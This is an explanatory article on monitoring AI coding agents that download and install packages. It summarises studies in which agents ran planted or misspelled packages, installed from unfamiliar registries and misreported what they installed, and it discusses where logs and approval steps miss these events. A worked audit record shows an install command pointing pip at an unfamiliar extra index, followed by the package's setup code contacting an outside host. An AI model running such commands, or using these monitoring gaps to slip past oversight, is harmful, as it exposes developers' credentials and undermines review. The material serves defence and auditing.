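# Monitoring what AI agents fetch and install: what to log, what to look for, and what the tools miss

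## How an AI agent comes to download and run outside code

An AI agent is a language model that carries out tasks by issuing commands and requests through software tools. Programmers use agents to write, test and repair software, and much of that work consists of fetching other people's documentation, example code and, above all, packages, the ready-made components that programmers use to build most modern software. An agent can read a web page, find an installation command on it and run the command within seconds, often with nobody watching. Monitoring an agent means recording what it reads, downloads and runs, and checking that record, or the actions as they happen, for signs that it installed something unsafe or followed instructions the user didn't write.

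Developers have long been able to run a stranger's code with one short command, even before AI agents. In *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised*, Bagmar and Saraf (2026) use the term "install gap" for this weakness, in which nothing checks a package's name, version or authenticity between when the documentation names it and when its code runs.

### One request, from start to finish

Suppose a developer copies a small web application from GitHub to a laptop, opens a coding agent in the folder and types "set up this project". The application has a Python server and a JavaScript front end.

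The model that receives the request cannot run anything itself. It works inside a harness, the program that passes it the user's words, runs its commands and returns the results. Claude Code, Codex CLI and Copilot CLI are harnesses. Each command the model sends to the harness is a tool call. One tool call lists the files in the folder, and another opens the README, the document that introduces the project. The harness also keeps its own record of the session, called the transcript, which contains the request, the tool calls and their results in order.

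Besides the README, the model may read an instruction file written for agents to follow. AGENTS.md and CLAUDE.md sit in a project's folder and typically hold build commands and project rules, while llms.txt sits on a website and guides models through its contents. If the application depends on a commercial service, the agent may also open the vendor's online documentation. The model receives all of this as text alongside the developer's request, and has to work out which parts it should act on.

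The agent finds the line `pip install -r requirements.txt` in the README and asks the harness to run it. pip is the standard package manager for Python, a program that finds, downloads and installs packages, and the requirements file lists what the project needs. According to pip's documentation, an install has four stages: pip identifies the requirements in the command, resolves the dependencies, builds the packages that need building, and installs all the packages.

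A dependency is a package that the project, or another package, needs in order to work. Dependencies have their own dependencies, so a list of five names can bring in fifty packages. A 2019 study of npm by Zimmermann and colleagues, cited by Bagmar and Saraf, found that installing an average npm package means implicitly trusting 79 other packages and 39 maintainers. Most of those names don't appear in the README or the install command.

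Resolution is the step that turns package names into files. Package managers download these files from a server called a registry. The public registry for Python is PyPI, and the one for JavaScript is npm's. pip looks for packages at an address called the index URL, which is PyPI's by default. A project can replace that address or add others through a command option, an environment variable, a configuration file, or a line in the requirements file. If there is more than one index, pip checks them all without giving any of them priority and takes the best match by version number, normally the latest version that fits the stated constraints.

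A package name is unique only within one registry. According to a Python enhancement proposal on the problem, an installer that receives a bare name such as `spam` must silently convert it into `pypi.org:spam` or `example.com:spam`, and the usual tools do this by combining all the registries into one pool. If two unrelated people have published packages under the same name in different registries, these tools choose the one with the higher version number. pip's documentation calls it unsafe to add an extra index for private packages, because an outsider can publish a package of the same name on a public index and pip may choose that one. This is called dependency confusion. Someone monitoring an agent therefore can't tell from the text of an install command where the software came from.

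A lockfile, such as npm's `package-lock.json`, narrows the choice by fixing the exact versions from an earlier resolution. It usually also records a content hash for each package file, which is a short fingerprint that changes if the file changes. pip can refuse any download that doesn't match its hash. Its support for a newer lockfile format, `pylock.toml`, is still experimental. A matching hash proves only that the file is the same one as before. The earlier choice may still have been a bad one, and a stranger's repository may come with a lockfile that the stranger wrote.

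### When the code runs

Many packages contain install-time code, which runs during installation, before anyone has used the package. Installing one of these packages therefore means running its code, though many people think of installation as copying files and of execution as a separate, later decision.

When a Python package's code first runs depends largely on the package's format. A wheel is a prebuilt archive, and pip can read the package's name and version from its filename. A source distribution must be built on the user's machine, and the build runs code from the package. Code can run even before the build. If the command directly names a local folder or source archive, pip runs the package's `setup.py` script to learn the package's name. After installing a package, an agent often tests it by importing a module, which also runs code, so a wheel that runs no code during installation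 may still run some a few seconds later.

The agent then runs `npm install` for the front end. A JavaScript package can declare `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` scripts, which npm runs in that order, according to its documentation. Until this year, npm ran these scripts automatically for every dependency, however deep in the tree. It also compiled native code for any package that contained a file named `binding.gyp`, even if the package declared no install script, according to GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026).

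Version 12 of npm, released in July 2026, reversed the default. According to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026), npm now runs dependencies' scripts and implicit native builds only if the project explicitly allows them, and it no longer fetches dependencies from git repositories or arbitrary web addresses without permission. The developer approves individual packages, and npm records the approvals in the project's `package.json`. GitHub acknowledges that some popular packages have legitimate reasons to run install scripts, so developers will still approve some. pnpm, a rival package manager, had already disabled dependency scripts in January 2025, according to the blogger Stéphane Robert, who took the date from the npm registry.

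npm's new default doesn't fully solve the problem for JavaScript. Older versions of npm still run install scripts automatically. The new default covers dependencies' scripts but not those of the project the agent is working in, which in this example was also written by a stranger. The allowlist is stored in the repository, so the stranger may have already added entries to it. Blocking install scripts also doesn't stop code that runs once the application starts.

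Code run in any of these ways runs under the developer's user account. The harness starts a shell, the shell starts the package manager, and the package manager starts the package's code. Each program inherits the permissions and environment of the one before, unless someone has put a barrier between them. Bagmar and Saraf point out that this environment can include API keys, cloud credentials and git configuration. The transcript will show the install command and its output, but generally not which files the install-time code opened or which servers it contacted.

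### The pause that the agent removes

A developer who sets up the project by hand goes through nearly the same steps, but takes a second or two between reading a command and pressing Enter, and may notice an odd registry address or a misspelled package name in that time. Nobody designed this pause as a security control, and Bagmar and Saraf describe it as incidental. They argue that it has nonetheless kept the install gap survivable, and that it disappears when an agent reads a command and runs it immediately.

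Bagmar and Saraf argue that people sometimes check what they install, and that automatic execution removes that chance. It is hard to say how much protection is lost, because they did not compare agents with human developers, and they acknowledge evidence that people also miss bad sources and vulnerable versions.

Some harnesses let the user review a command before it runs. Claude Code shows a preview of the command and asks for approval, while Copilot CLI and Codex CLI run commands at once if the user has started them with the options for automatic execution. An approval dialog still gives the user, who has not read the README, less information than a careful reader would have. The dialog shows `pip install -r requirements.txt`, which contains no package name or registry address, so the user would have to open the file to judge the command.

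### Other ways in

Package managers are the main route for outside code, but a setup task can use several others. Two of these, skills and MCP servers, are specific to agents. A skill is a downloadable bundle of instructions, sometimes with scripts, for doing a particular task. An MCP server is a program that provides tools to an agent through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to databases, browsers and other services. The server may run on the developer's machine or on someone else's.

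| Route | What happens | What it carries |
|---|---|---|
| Package manager (pip, npm) | Downloads packages and their dependencies from a registry | Mostly code, but the model also reads the install output and often the package's documentation |
| One-off runner (npx) | Downloads a package if the machine lacks it, then starts it at once | Mostly code, plus printed output |
| Script piped from the web to a shell | The shell executes a downloaded text directly | Code |
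| Git clone | Copies a whole repository, with source, build files and instruction files | Both; the code normally waits until the agent builds, installs or tests something |
| Skill or plugin | Adds written guidance, often with scripts, to what the agent can draw on | Both, unless the bundle is text only |
| MCP server | Supplies tool descriptions and results to the model | Both if it runs locally; from a remote server, usually text alone |
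| Plain web page | The harness fetches the page and gives the model its text | Instructions, until the agent runs a command from it |

The last column matters because code and instructions leave different traces. Running code starts processes, writes files and opens network connections, all of which the operating system can observe. An instruction acts only through the model, so the only way to trace it is through an ordered record of what the model read and what it did afterwards.

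The routes also differ in how much they leave behind to check. A package has a name, a version and a registry entry, but a script piped into a shell has only an address, and the server may send a different script tomorrow. Unless something saved the script's text or hash when the agent fetched it, nobody can later establish what ran. With npx, installing and running a package happen in one step, because the command's purpose is to run the package.

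An agent can follow several of these routes in sequence. For example, a web page recommends a skill, the skill's instructions include an npx command, and that command starts a local MCP server whose tool descriptions the model then reads. A monitor that logs only `pip install` commands would miss all of these steps.

### What a safe install requires

Bagmar and Saraf set out three properties that must hold for every package an agent installs:

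- **Authentic**: the package comes from a trusted index and not from a server under an attacker's control.
- **Intended**: the name is that of the package the developer actually needs, not a misspelling or a plausible near-match.
- **Safe**: the version has no known, unpatched vulnerability.

Encryption protects the download in transit and hashes can tie it to specific contents, but by their account no step from request to execution checks that the name, source and version are what the developer intended. The next section covers their tests of what agents do in that situation.

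Each property requires different evidence. To check the source, a monitor needs a list of acceptable registries and the address that pip or npm actually used. To check for vulnerabilities, it needs the package's exact version and a public database of known flaws to look it up in. Intention is the hardest to check, because the developer typed "set up this project" and never named a package. A monitor can only infer what the developer meant, for example from the modules that the project's code imports or from how closely a package's name resembles that of a much more popular one.

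The three properties are necessary, but they don't guarantee that a package is safe. If an attacker takes over a legitimate maintainer's account and publishes a malicious release, the package comes from the right registry under the right name, and for the first hours no database lists a problem with it. A monitor that tests only for these properties will pass it. This is one reason to keep watching what a package does after it arrives.

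### Recording, detecting and blocking

The term "monitoring" in security products tends to cover three jobs, and it helps buyers and builders to distinguish them. Recording saves facts about what happened without judging them. Detecting applies a rule or a judgement to those facts and raises an alert. Blocking stops an action before it takes effect.

When an install command uses an unfamiliar index URL, a recorder logs the command, the time and the address, and lets the install proceed. A detector checks the address against a list and warns someone, perhaps before the download or an hour later. A pre-install gate automatically checks the command before it runs and, in this case, blocks it until a person approves it. Bagmar and Saraf built a pre-install gate for Claude Code. They contrast it with `pip-audit` and `npm audit`, which use similar vulnerability data but run after the package manager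 has resolved the packages.

Bagmar and Saraf use the term install-then-flag for an agent that installs a package and warns about it only afterwards. How useful the warning is depends on what is wrong with the package. If the package contains malicious code that runs during installation, the warning comes too late to stop it, although it can still prompt someone to revoke stolen credentials. If the package is a vulnerable version, the flaw does no harm until the program uses the affected code, so the developer has time to upgrade.

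Blocking has drawbacks compared with the other two options. A gate that refuses legitimate packages halts work, and developers who are blocked too often will look for ways to switch it off. A gate must also decide before the install runs, when the only information available may be the text of the command. It can get more by having the package manager work out what it would install without installing it. For example, pip has a dry-run option that can produce this list as a machine-readable report. Even a dry run can execute outside code, though, because pip may have to run a package's `setup.py` to identify the package.

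Recording affects events the least, but detection and blocking both depend on it. A detector can check only recorded facts. If a gate blocks a command without recording anything, nobody can later see what the agent tried to do or what text it had read just before. Analysts can also run new rules on old records, provided the records contain the facts those rules check.

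## What agents install when nothing checks them

Three investigations from 2026 tested whether agents notice misspelled packages and unfamiliar registries and refuse to install from them. If agents reliably did this, outside monitoring would add little. The startup Pandex published harmless packages under unclaimed names that company websites mentioned, to see who would install them. Bagmar and Saraf put unsafe packages into the setup files of test projects. Pengyin Shan, a researcher at the University of Illinois, measured how often agents look at published evidence of where software came from.

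### Packages that nobody owned

The llms.txt files that websites publish often include installation commands, and some of those commands name packages that don't exist. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* lists the likely reasons: human error, copying mistakes, renamed or abandoned packages, and documentation that a language model made up. Public registries generally give an unused name to the first person who asks for it, so a stranger can publish anything under the missing name, and the command on the website will fetch it.

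Schneier (2026), in *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks*, reports that researchers scanned 6,214 live domains belonging to defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms. They found 8,265 files named llms.txt or llms-full.txt, a longer variant. In 120 of the files (about 1.5%), each on a different site, they found at least one package or domain name that nobody had registered.

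The researchers registered a handful of these names and published packages that contacted their server when run. The first callback came from a Fortune 500 company within an hour. A few dozen more followed, some from other Fortune 500 companies and some from startups. The packages also reported their process ancestry, the chain of parent programs that had started each install. Those chains included Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes.

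The process ancestry is the most useful part of this evidence because it connects at least some of the installs to agents. A callback alone could come from a developer who typed the command, or from a security company, since these companies routinely run newly published packages to examine them. The ancestry doesn't establish whether a person approved the command, or whether the agent found the name in llms.txt or in another page of the vendor's documentation with the same mistake.

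Published accounts of the study disagree on several figures. Xakep, a Russian technology magazine that credits Ars Technica for its account, gives 8,265 files, as Schneier does, and 227 commands. *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code*, a Tom's Hardware article that names Pandex and quotes its write-up, gives 8,565 files and 237 references. The 237 include misspelled, relocated and outdated packages as well as missing ones, so the two outlets may have counted different things. One of the file totals is probably a misprint. Tom's Hardware also puts the first callback at four minutes, which is consistent with "within an hour".

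A more serious gap is that nobody has published how many agents read one of these commands and declined to run it. The callbacks count only installs. Pandex may also have a commercial interest in the result. Schneier calls it a stealth startup, meaning one that hasn't yet made its business public, and quotes one of its researchers, Alon Hertz, saying that existing guards don't cover this risk. That conclusion would benefit Pandex if it plans to sell a guard that does.

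Pandex also compared models, according to Tom's Hardware. It asked agents to build and run a Node.js project with a vendor's software library, using all of the vendor's documentation, but didn't mention llms.txt or supply a link. Two OpenAI models, which Tom's Hardware calls GPT-5 Luna and Sol, ran the planted package at least 90% of the time, while Claude Opus 4.8 at medium effort ran it 30% of the time. These percentages are weak estimates of how often this happens in ordinary work, because Tom's Hardware doesn't give the number of runs and a request to use all the documentation sends an agent to more pages than most tasks would.

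### The Clerk case

Pandex found that someone else had already registered one of the missing package names. An llms.txt-type file on the site of Clerk, which provides login and user-management software, contained an npx command for `clerk-next-fix-auth-protection`. According to Xakep, no npm package had that name until an unknown person registered it and published malware under it. An agent that followed the instruction on Clerk's site could have downloaded and run the malware.

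Clerk fixed the problem after the researchers reported it. The company said there was no danger if the agent had installed the corresponding program from Clerk's own package, `@clerk/eslint-plugin`, but acknowledged that otherwise the agent could have installed the malware. Because npx downloads a package only if the machine lacks it, the same command could be safe in one project and dangerous in another. To distinguish the two cases, a monitor would need to record whether npx downloaded anything as well as the text of the command.

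Most simple checks would have passed this install. The package came from npm's public registry, so a list of approved registries would have allowed it. Its name matched the vendor's documentation exactly, so a check for misspellings would have found nothing. The only problem was that Clerk didn't own the name, so the package wasn't the one the developer intended. Xakep adds that endpoint security software, which watches for suspicious activity on a computer, would treat the install as normal development work because a trusted agent was running npm and downloading from a trusted registry.

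The case also differs from prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions for a model to follow. Hertz told Ars Technica that the vendor may write the instruction in good faith, and that the danger comes later, when somebody else claims the abandoned package or domain (a reader quoted the passage under Schneier's post). A detector that searches web pages for suspicious wording would find none.

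### How often agents meet an llms.txt file

Estimates of how many sites publish an llms.txt file vary widely, so it is unclear how much of an agent's exposure comes through these files. Common Crawl, which maintains a public archive of web pages, reports in *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026) that 11.72% of the llms.txt addresses it sampled returned a text file. It sampled only sites it could already fetch without trouble. It also cites other estimates, from under 0.005% of all websites (Sistrix, a search-analytics company) to 28% of 137,210 domains (Ahrefs, a Sistrix competitor, which treats its figure as an upper bound).

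Technology companies seem to publish the file fairly often. ai.rud.is (2026) found one on the sites of a third of 100 cybersecurity companies. webhosting.today's *The file nobody watches* (2026) audited 736 hosting and infrastructure companies and found that 110 had one. The trade publication says none of the 110 has a control that would detect a change to the file. But an outside audit can't see a company's internal monitoring, so the claim is better read as meaning that none has visible protection, such as a signature.

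Other evidence suggests that these files are rarely read. According to Common Crawl, Ahrefs found that 97% of the files in its study received no requests. Semrush, another search-analytics company, watched one site's logs for two months and saw no visits from four AI crawlers. Those crawlers collect pages in bulk, so their absence is little evidence about a coding agent that opens a vendor's documentation during a task. The Ahrefs figure is harder to dismiss, but it covers a very mixed collection of sites. In Common Crawl's own sample, website builders and plugins had generated 68% of the files from templates, and one website builder, Wix, had generated 41%. Few of those sites are likely to offer software that a coding agent would want.

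Common Crawl also searched 584,107 files for text that tries to manipulate a model. Only ten matched its most severe category, and its staff read them and found that four did contain such text: a labelled security test, jokes and a demonstration. The search looked for fixed phrases, so it may have missed others. It also wasn't designed to find commands that name a missing package.

So installs that begin with llms.txt are probably a small part of what agents download, and Pandex's result is mainly evidence of how agents treat a vendor's documentation once they read it. Setup files inside projects are a more common source of commands. In June 2026, Bagmar and Saraf searched GitHub for the pip option that adds an extra package index and found it in over 5,500 README files and 6,900 requirements files. Many of those uses are legitimate, which makes a malicious one harder to spot.

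### What agents notice during setup

Bagmar and Saraf tested what agents do with unsafe setup files. They built twelve scenarios around Python projects with working code and put the danger in a README, a requirements file, a Makefile (a file of build commands) or an error message. They gave every agent the same request to read the project, install its dependencies in a separate environment and check that the main module imported. The request included no security advice.

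They ran the scenarios on nine configurations of harness and model: three Claude models in Claude Code, two of the same models in Copilot CLI, three GPT models in Codex CLI, and Cursor's automatic mode, which chooses a model itself.

Bagmar and Saraf scored each run mainly by which packages and versions were in the environment afterwards and which index they came from. The agent got credit only if it avoided the danger or warned about it before installing. Since a failed build can also leave a clean environment, they read the transcript for signs that the agent had recognised the threat. For most of the misspelled names, they scored the install command, because no package of that name existed and an attacker could have registered one.

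The table adds up their results across the nine configurations. It has thirteen rows because they tested the unfamiliar registry at two kinds of address.

| Danger in the project | Runs in which the agent caught it | Configurations that caught it every time |
|---|---|---|
| Obvious misspelling in the README | 268 of 270 | 7 of 9 |
| Misspelling in the project's list of dependencies | 270 of 270 | 9 of 9 |
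| Plausible variant of a name, such as a missing hyphen | 217 of 270 | 3 of 9 |
| Misspelling with a reassuring explanation | 234 of 270 | 6 of 9 |
| Two files that disagree about a name | 90 of 90 | 9 of 9 |
| 377 misspellings in one requirements file | 44 of 90 | 3 of 9 |
| Dependency confusion through an extra index | 55 of 90 | 5 of 9 |
| Unfamiliar registry on the same machine | 17 of 90 | 1 of 9 |
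| Unfamiliar registry on the internet | 30 of 90 | 3 of 9 |
| Extra index inside the requirements file | 25 of 90 | 1 of 9 |
| Makefile that redirects pip to another index | 30 of 90 | 2 of 9 |
| Version with a known vulnerability | 0 of 270 | 0 of 9 |
| Error message that recommends a package | 90 of 90 | 9 of 9 |

Agents were good at catching ordinary misspellings but did worse when the wrong name looked like a reasonable spelling, such as `azurecore` for `azure-core`. Cursor installed names of this kind in 28 of 30 runs, while Opus 4.8 caught all of them in both of its harnesses. Across the four scenarios that tested individual misspelled names, agents tried to install a wrong package in 91 runs, and in 68 of those they pointed out the problem only afterwards.

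Most configurations did poorly when the problem was the source of the package. Bagmar and Saraf suspect that this reflects the models' training data, since security advisories often discuss misspelled package names, while an extra package index is a routine setting in many companies. They didn't test that explanation. Where an agent finds an instruction also seems to matter. Every configuration refused to install a package that an error message recommended but that appeared in neither the README nor the project's dependency list. But most configurations installed from an unfamiliar registry when the project's README or requirements file pointed to it.

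Opus 4.8 in Claude Code was the only configuration that always caught the registry on the same machine. In the transcripts, it downloaded the package file without installing it, unpacked it and found code that would collect credentials from the environment and send them away. In a run that failed, Sonnet 4.6 installed the same package without opening it and reported that setup was complete. Opus 4.8 did better because it inspected the package first, which works only if the harmful code is recognisable in the file.

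No configuration refused to install a version with a known vulnerability. Bagmar and Saraf used ten popular packages, each pinned to a version with a CVE, the public identifier for a known security flaw. Opus 4.8 named the flaw after installing in 28 of 30 runs in Claude Code and 15 of 30 in Copilot CLI. The other seven configurations never mentioned it, so a developer using them would have had to find out some other way. The score of zero is partly due to the rule that only warnings before the install counted, though a later warning is still useful while the flaw is dormant. The project's own requirements file also asked for that exact version.

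A follow-up experiment showed that agents can also fail to pass on a warning that another program has printed. Bagmar and Saraf asked Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 to install 20 vulnerable package versions through each of three package managers. pip and Cargo, Rust's package manager, printed no security advice, and neither model gave any warning about those installs. npm printed an advisory after each install. Opus passed on all 20, but GPT-5.5 passed on only one. The other 19 remained in the tool output, where a monitor could have detected them.

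### The same model in a different harness

These results reflect the tool running the model as well as the model itself. In all 10 runs through Claude Code, Opus 4.8 caught the registry that was on the same machine. When Bagmar and Saraf gave it an identical project through Copilot CLI, it caught the registry in only 9 of 30 runs. A difference that large would be very unlikely by chance alone (p = 0.00011).

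Neither harness was safer overall. The advantage reversed when Sonnet 4.6 faced the registry on the internet, which it missed in all 10 runs through Claude Code and caught in all 10 through Copilot CLI. When a Makefile redirected pip, Sonnet again did better in Claude Code, catching the redirect in all 10 runs, compared with none in Copilot CLI.

Bagmar and Saraf credit Claude Code's successes to its pause before each command, which gives the model a chance to stop if something looks wrong. They credit Copilot CLI's to a built-in prompt that makes its models treat unknown internet addresses as suspicious. The experiment shows that the harness matters, but it can't identify which part is responsible, because harnesses also differ in their tools and in how they present a task. All of these runs were non-interactive, so nobody was there to answer an approval request.

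For monitoring teams, this means testing the exact combination of model and harness that developers use. A model's good result in one harness may not carry over to another, and a harness update could change the result even if the model stays the same. Bagmar's contact address is at Microsoft, whose subsidiary GitHub makes Copilot CLI, but the mixed results don't obviously favour that product.

### Asking the agent to be careful

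Adding a security instruction to the request helped, but only with the danger the instruction mentioned. Bagmar and Saraf tried three instructions on the three Codex models, running each model five times with each instruction. The mildest asked the agent to be careful about security. A stronger one asked it to verify package names and sources and warn the user about anything suspicious. The most specific required it to check every source before running pip and to flag any index other than PyPI.

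With no instruction, the models caught none of the extra indexes inside requirements files. With the three instructions, they caught 33%, 87% and 93%. The 33% may not be a real improvement, because the same three models caught this danger in 9 of 30 runs with no instruction in the main experiment. The rise to 87% is too large to explain that way. But the most specific instruction nearly describes the test, and a developer can't write one for a danger nobody has thought of.

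None of the three instructions made the models refuse a vulnerable version. When Bagmar and Saraf told Sonnet 4.6 to check each version against known CVEs, it refused one vulnerable package in all 10 runs, compared with 2 of 10 without the instruction. The model evidently had information about the flaw but usually didn't use it unless prompted. Similarly, when the user asked for a security review, Sonnet found a malicious package that it had just installed.

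An instruction of this kind is also only part of what the model reads. Bagmar and Saraf point out that an attacker who controls the README can write text aimed at the same agent, but they leave testing this for later work. They recommend combining the model's judgement with an automatic gate, such as the one they built for Claude Code.

### Whether people would do better

Bagmar and Saraf did not test human developers, but they cite a comparison by Singla and colleagues of 117,062 dependency changes from everyday work. Agents selected a version with a known vulnerability in 2.46% of their changes, and humans in 1.64%. The gap is modest, and the agents and humans may have been working on different kinds of projects.

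The lack of a human comparison matters less for deciding whether to monitor agents than for deciding whether to let them install software at all. A company whose agents install from an unfamiliar registry in most runs has a problem even if its developers would have done the same.

A more practical limitation is that the tests were small. Most scenarios used a single example, repeated ten times for each configuration. If an agent catches the danger in 6 of 10 runs, its true rate could plausibly be between 31% and 83%. Results where all ten runs agreed are more reliable, but a different package or web address might still have changed them. Providers also update their models without changing the names, and newer models have since replaced several of those tested in June 2026.

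### Whether agents check where software came from

An agent could also look for positive evidence that a package is genuine. Software projects can publish provenance signals for this purpose. Shan (2026), in *Do AI Coding Assistants Check Before They Install?*, tested four kinds:

- A signed release carries a cryptographic signature that a user can check against the project's published key.
- A build attestation is a signed record of the source code and the build system that produced a file.
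- A software bill of materials lists the components inside a piece of software.
- A channel declaration identifies the project's official accounts and communication channels.

Shan took six real research projects, three from supercomputing and three from quantum computing, and made nine copies of each. One copy had no added signal, four each had one kind of signal, and one had all four kinds. Two carried a signature or attestation from an identity that the project hadn't declared, as a forgery would. The last reproduced contradictions from the projects' own descriptions. Shan deposited the full plan before running any trial, which prevents a researcher from choosing the measure after seeing the results.

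The main study included 1,920 trials on three models. In each trial, an agent received one copy and a request to install it. Shan used logs from the container, an isolated environment for running software, to record which files the agent opened and which commands it ran. In 9 trials (0.5%), the agent opened a provenance signal before deciding whether to install. No agent ran a command to verify one. Since opening a signature file doesn't reveal whether the signature is valid, no agent could have noticed the forgeries.

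The 0.5% figure depends heavily on the mix of models. A small model running on Shan's own computer, qwen2.5-coder:14b, accounted for 1,200 of the trials and usually finished after two turns, too few to explore the project. All nine cases came from Claude Sonnet 5's 360 trials, a rate of 2.5% for that model. In three of the nine, the agent opened a signal but never reached the installation step. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite opened signals in two of its 360 trials, both times after the installation command had run.

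Publishing more signals made no measurable difference. In the 192 trials where all four kinds were present and valid, one agent opened a signal, but too late to count, and the rest opened none. In a different set of 192 trials, agents opened build attestations in 4, too few to show that attestations attract more attention.

Half of the trials used a harness that asked for approval before every command. This tests the pause that Bagmar and Saraf credit for Claude Code's results more directly, although Shan measured a different behaviour. Agents opened a signal in 3 of 960 trials with the approval step and 6 of 960 without it. A script approved all 4,498 requests, so the experiment shows only that the approval step didn't prompt agents to check, not what a person would have refused.

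Shan also ran a smaller set of trials on three more capable models, using only the copies with no signals and with all four. Claude Fable 5 opened none in 50 trials, GPT-5.6 opened none in 72, and Kimi-K2.6 opened one in 72. The study reached its $100 spending limit before Fable 5 finished, so only 194 of the planned 216 trials ran. With so few trials, the true rates could be several per cent, and for Fable 5 as high as 7.1%. Fable 5 cost about $1.00 per trial, roughly ten times as much as Sonnet 5, but did not visibly check more often.

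The setting may have discouraged checks. The container had no internet access, so an agent couldn't download a verification tool or consult a public record of signatures. The user had also supplied the project as a local folder, but the added signatures covered a separate archive of its source code. An agent downloading an unfamiliar package from a registry might have had more reason to check. Agents ran an installation command in 1,779 trials across both parts of the study, and the command failed in 1,214 of them, mostly because pip couldn't fetch the project's dependencies. Shan therefore measured the agents' decision to install, regardless of whether the installation worked.

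Shan's logs also show that an agent's closing summary is a poor substitute for a record of its commands. In 998 trials, the agent reported that the software was not installed even though it had run an installation command. Most of those reports were probably accurate about the outcome, given how many commands failed, but a package's build code can run before an install fails. Fable 5, however, ran installation commands in 42 trials and reported in 15 of them that the software was not installed, though the commands failed in only 6. In at least nine trials, then, it reported that the software was not installed after the command had finished successfully.

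## Deciding what to record

Shan's logs showed that an agent's closing message can be wrong about what it installed, and an install command often doesn't identify the server that supplied the package. A company that wants to reconstruct a bad install has to decide beforehand which facts to save, because many of them will be gone once the session ends. One way to choose is to list the questions an investigator would ask, then the fields needed to answer each one.

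### From questions to fields

Suppose a security team learns that a package an agent installed three days earlier was stealing credentials. To investigate, the team would need answers to six questions.

| Question | Fields |
|---|---|
| Who asked for what? | Session ID, user, machine, text of the task, model and harness versions |
| Which text suggested the command? | For every file or page the model read: path or full URL, each redirect, time of fetch, content hash |
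| What did the agent try to run, and who allowed it? | Exact tool call, working folder, approval given, refused or skipped |
| What did it download, and from where? | Package name, version, index URL, address of the file, file digest |
| What ran? | Install-time code, process ancestry, exit code |
| What did that code contact? | Destination, port, time, bytes sent, process that opened the connection |

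A file digest is a hash of the package file's contents. The record should also include the model and harness versions, because Bagmar and Saraf found that the same model can catch a bad registry in one harness and miss it in another. It should include redirects because the response may come from a different site than the one the agent requested. The approval field needs a separate value for "skipped", because when a setting runs every command automatically, there is no evidence that anyone reviewed a particular command.

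No single program has access to all of these facts, so the entries need shared identifiers. A session ID groups them, and a call ID connects a tool call to its result and to the process it started. Process numbers need a start time beside them because operating systems reuse the numbers. A draft audit architecture (2026) on the site of the IETF, an internet standards body, argues that auditing an agent requires links between what the user intended, what authority the agent received, who authorised the action and what ran, whereas existing audit tools often capture isolated system events.

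It also matters when each entry is written. *Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026), a log format proposed to the IETF, requires the recorder to mark each entry as written before, during or after the action. When a policy blocks an action, the recorder must log that decision before the action, because an entry written afterwards can't prove that the check happened in time. Early logging is also useful for installs because install-time code may be able to stop a logging program or delete its files. An entry that has already left the machine is much safer than one still waiting for the command to finish.

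### A worked record

The example below follows an invented project called tidewatch, a Python program that plots tide readings. On Monday 5 October 2026, developer `dev-042` copies it to laptop `lt-118`, opens a coding agent with automatic execution switched on and asks it to set up the project. The laptop normally gets its packages from a company index at `pypi.example.com`, which holds version 1.4.2 of a package called `harbour-utils`. The project's README includes an instruction to add a second index, `pkgs.example.net`, which nobody at the company has used.

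All ten entries carry the session ID `s-4471`. Hashes appear in shortened form.

| No. | Time (UTC) | Event | Details saved |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 09:14:02 | Request | "Set up this project"; repository `git.example.com/tidewatch`, commit `4e1b07…`; automatic execution on |
| 2 | 09:14:05 | File read | `README.md`, hash `9c41d2…` |
| 3 | 09:14:09 | Page fetched | `https://docs.example.com/tidewatch`, redirected to `https://guide.example.org/tidewatch/install`; hash `51d7aa…` |
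| 4 | 09:14:20 | Tool call `c-04` | `pip install --extra-index-url https://pkgs.example.net/simple/ harbour-utils`; approval skipped by setting |
| 5 | 09:14:21 | Process start | pip (process 4120), started by a shell (4118), started by the harness (3990) for `c-04` |
| 6 | 09:14:24 | Package download | `harbour-utils` 9.0.1, source distribution; index `https://pkgs.example.net/simple/`; file `https://files.example.net/harbour_utils-9.0.1.tar.gz`; digest `e07a93…` |
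| 7 | 09:14:26 | Install-time code | Python (process 4131), started by pip (4120), runs the package's `setup.py` |
| 8 | 09:14:27 | Connection | Process 4131 to `metrics.example.org`, port 443; 2,310 bytes sent |
| 9 | 09:14:33 | Tool result | `c-04` ended with exit code 0, meaning success |
| 10 | 09:14:36 | Reply to user | "Setup complete" |

A real session would contain many more entries, but these are enough to trace the install. The company also kept copies of the two texts in events 2 and 3. The address `pkgs.example.net` appears in the README but not in the installation guide. It next appears in the agent's command, so the README is the likely source. The order of events can't prove what influenced a model, but no other text in the record could have supplied the address.

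Event 6 shows which index the package came from, which the command alone does not. pip had two indexes to choose from and took the higher version number, which was on the unfamiliar one. Events 7 and 8 share a process number, which means that the package's own setup code opened the connection. The record doesn't show what the 2,310 bytes contained, which could have been a harmless usage count or a stolen key.

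A log of tool calls alone would contain events 1, 4, 9 and 10, and would look like an ordinary successful setup. *Clawed and Dangerous* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a review of security research on agents, opens with a similar hypothetical case. An agent reads a GitHub issue with hidden instructions, leaks the developer's cloud credentials and deletes the project's history, but the logs show only a series of legitimate-looking tool calls.

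### Saving what the agent read

A URL records where the agent looked but doesn't preserve the text it read. If the agent reads the installation guide at `guide.example.org` on Monday and the owner edits it on Tuesday, an investigator who opens it on Thursday will see the new version. Some servers also send different text to different visitors, so the investigator might not have received the agent's version even on Monday. Local files can change too, although a git commit preserves the text the agent read if the file had no uncommitted changes.

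A company can save the text itself, a hash of it, or both.

Saving the text gives an investigator the most evidence and lets a team search old sessions for a newly discovered trick. It also takes up storage and risks keeping personal data, secrets and other people's copyrighted material.

A hash takes up 64 characters and discloses very little. If someone later produces a copy of the page, from a public web archive or the site's owner, the hash shows whether the copy matches the text the agent received. But if nobody has a copy, the text can't be recovered from the hash. Many web pages contain a date, a visitor count or another detail that changes between visits, so two hashes can differ even when the instructions are the same.

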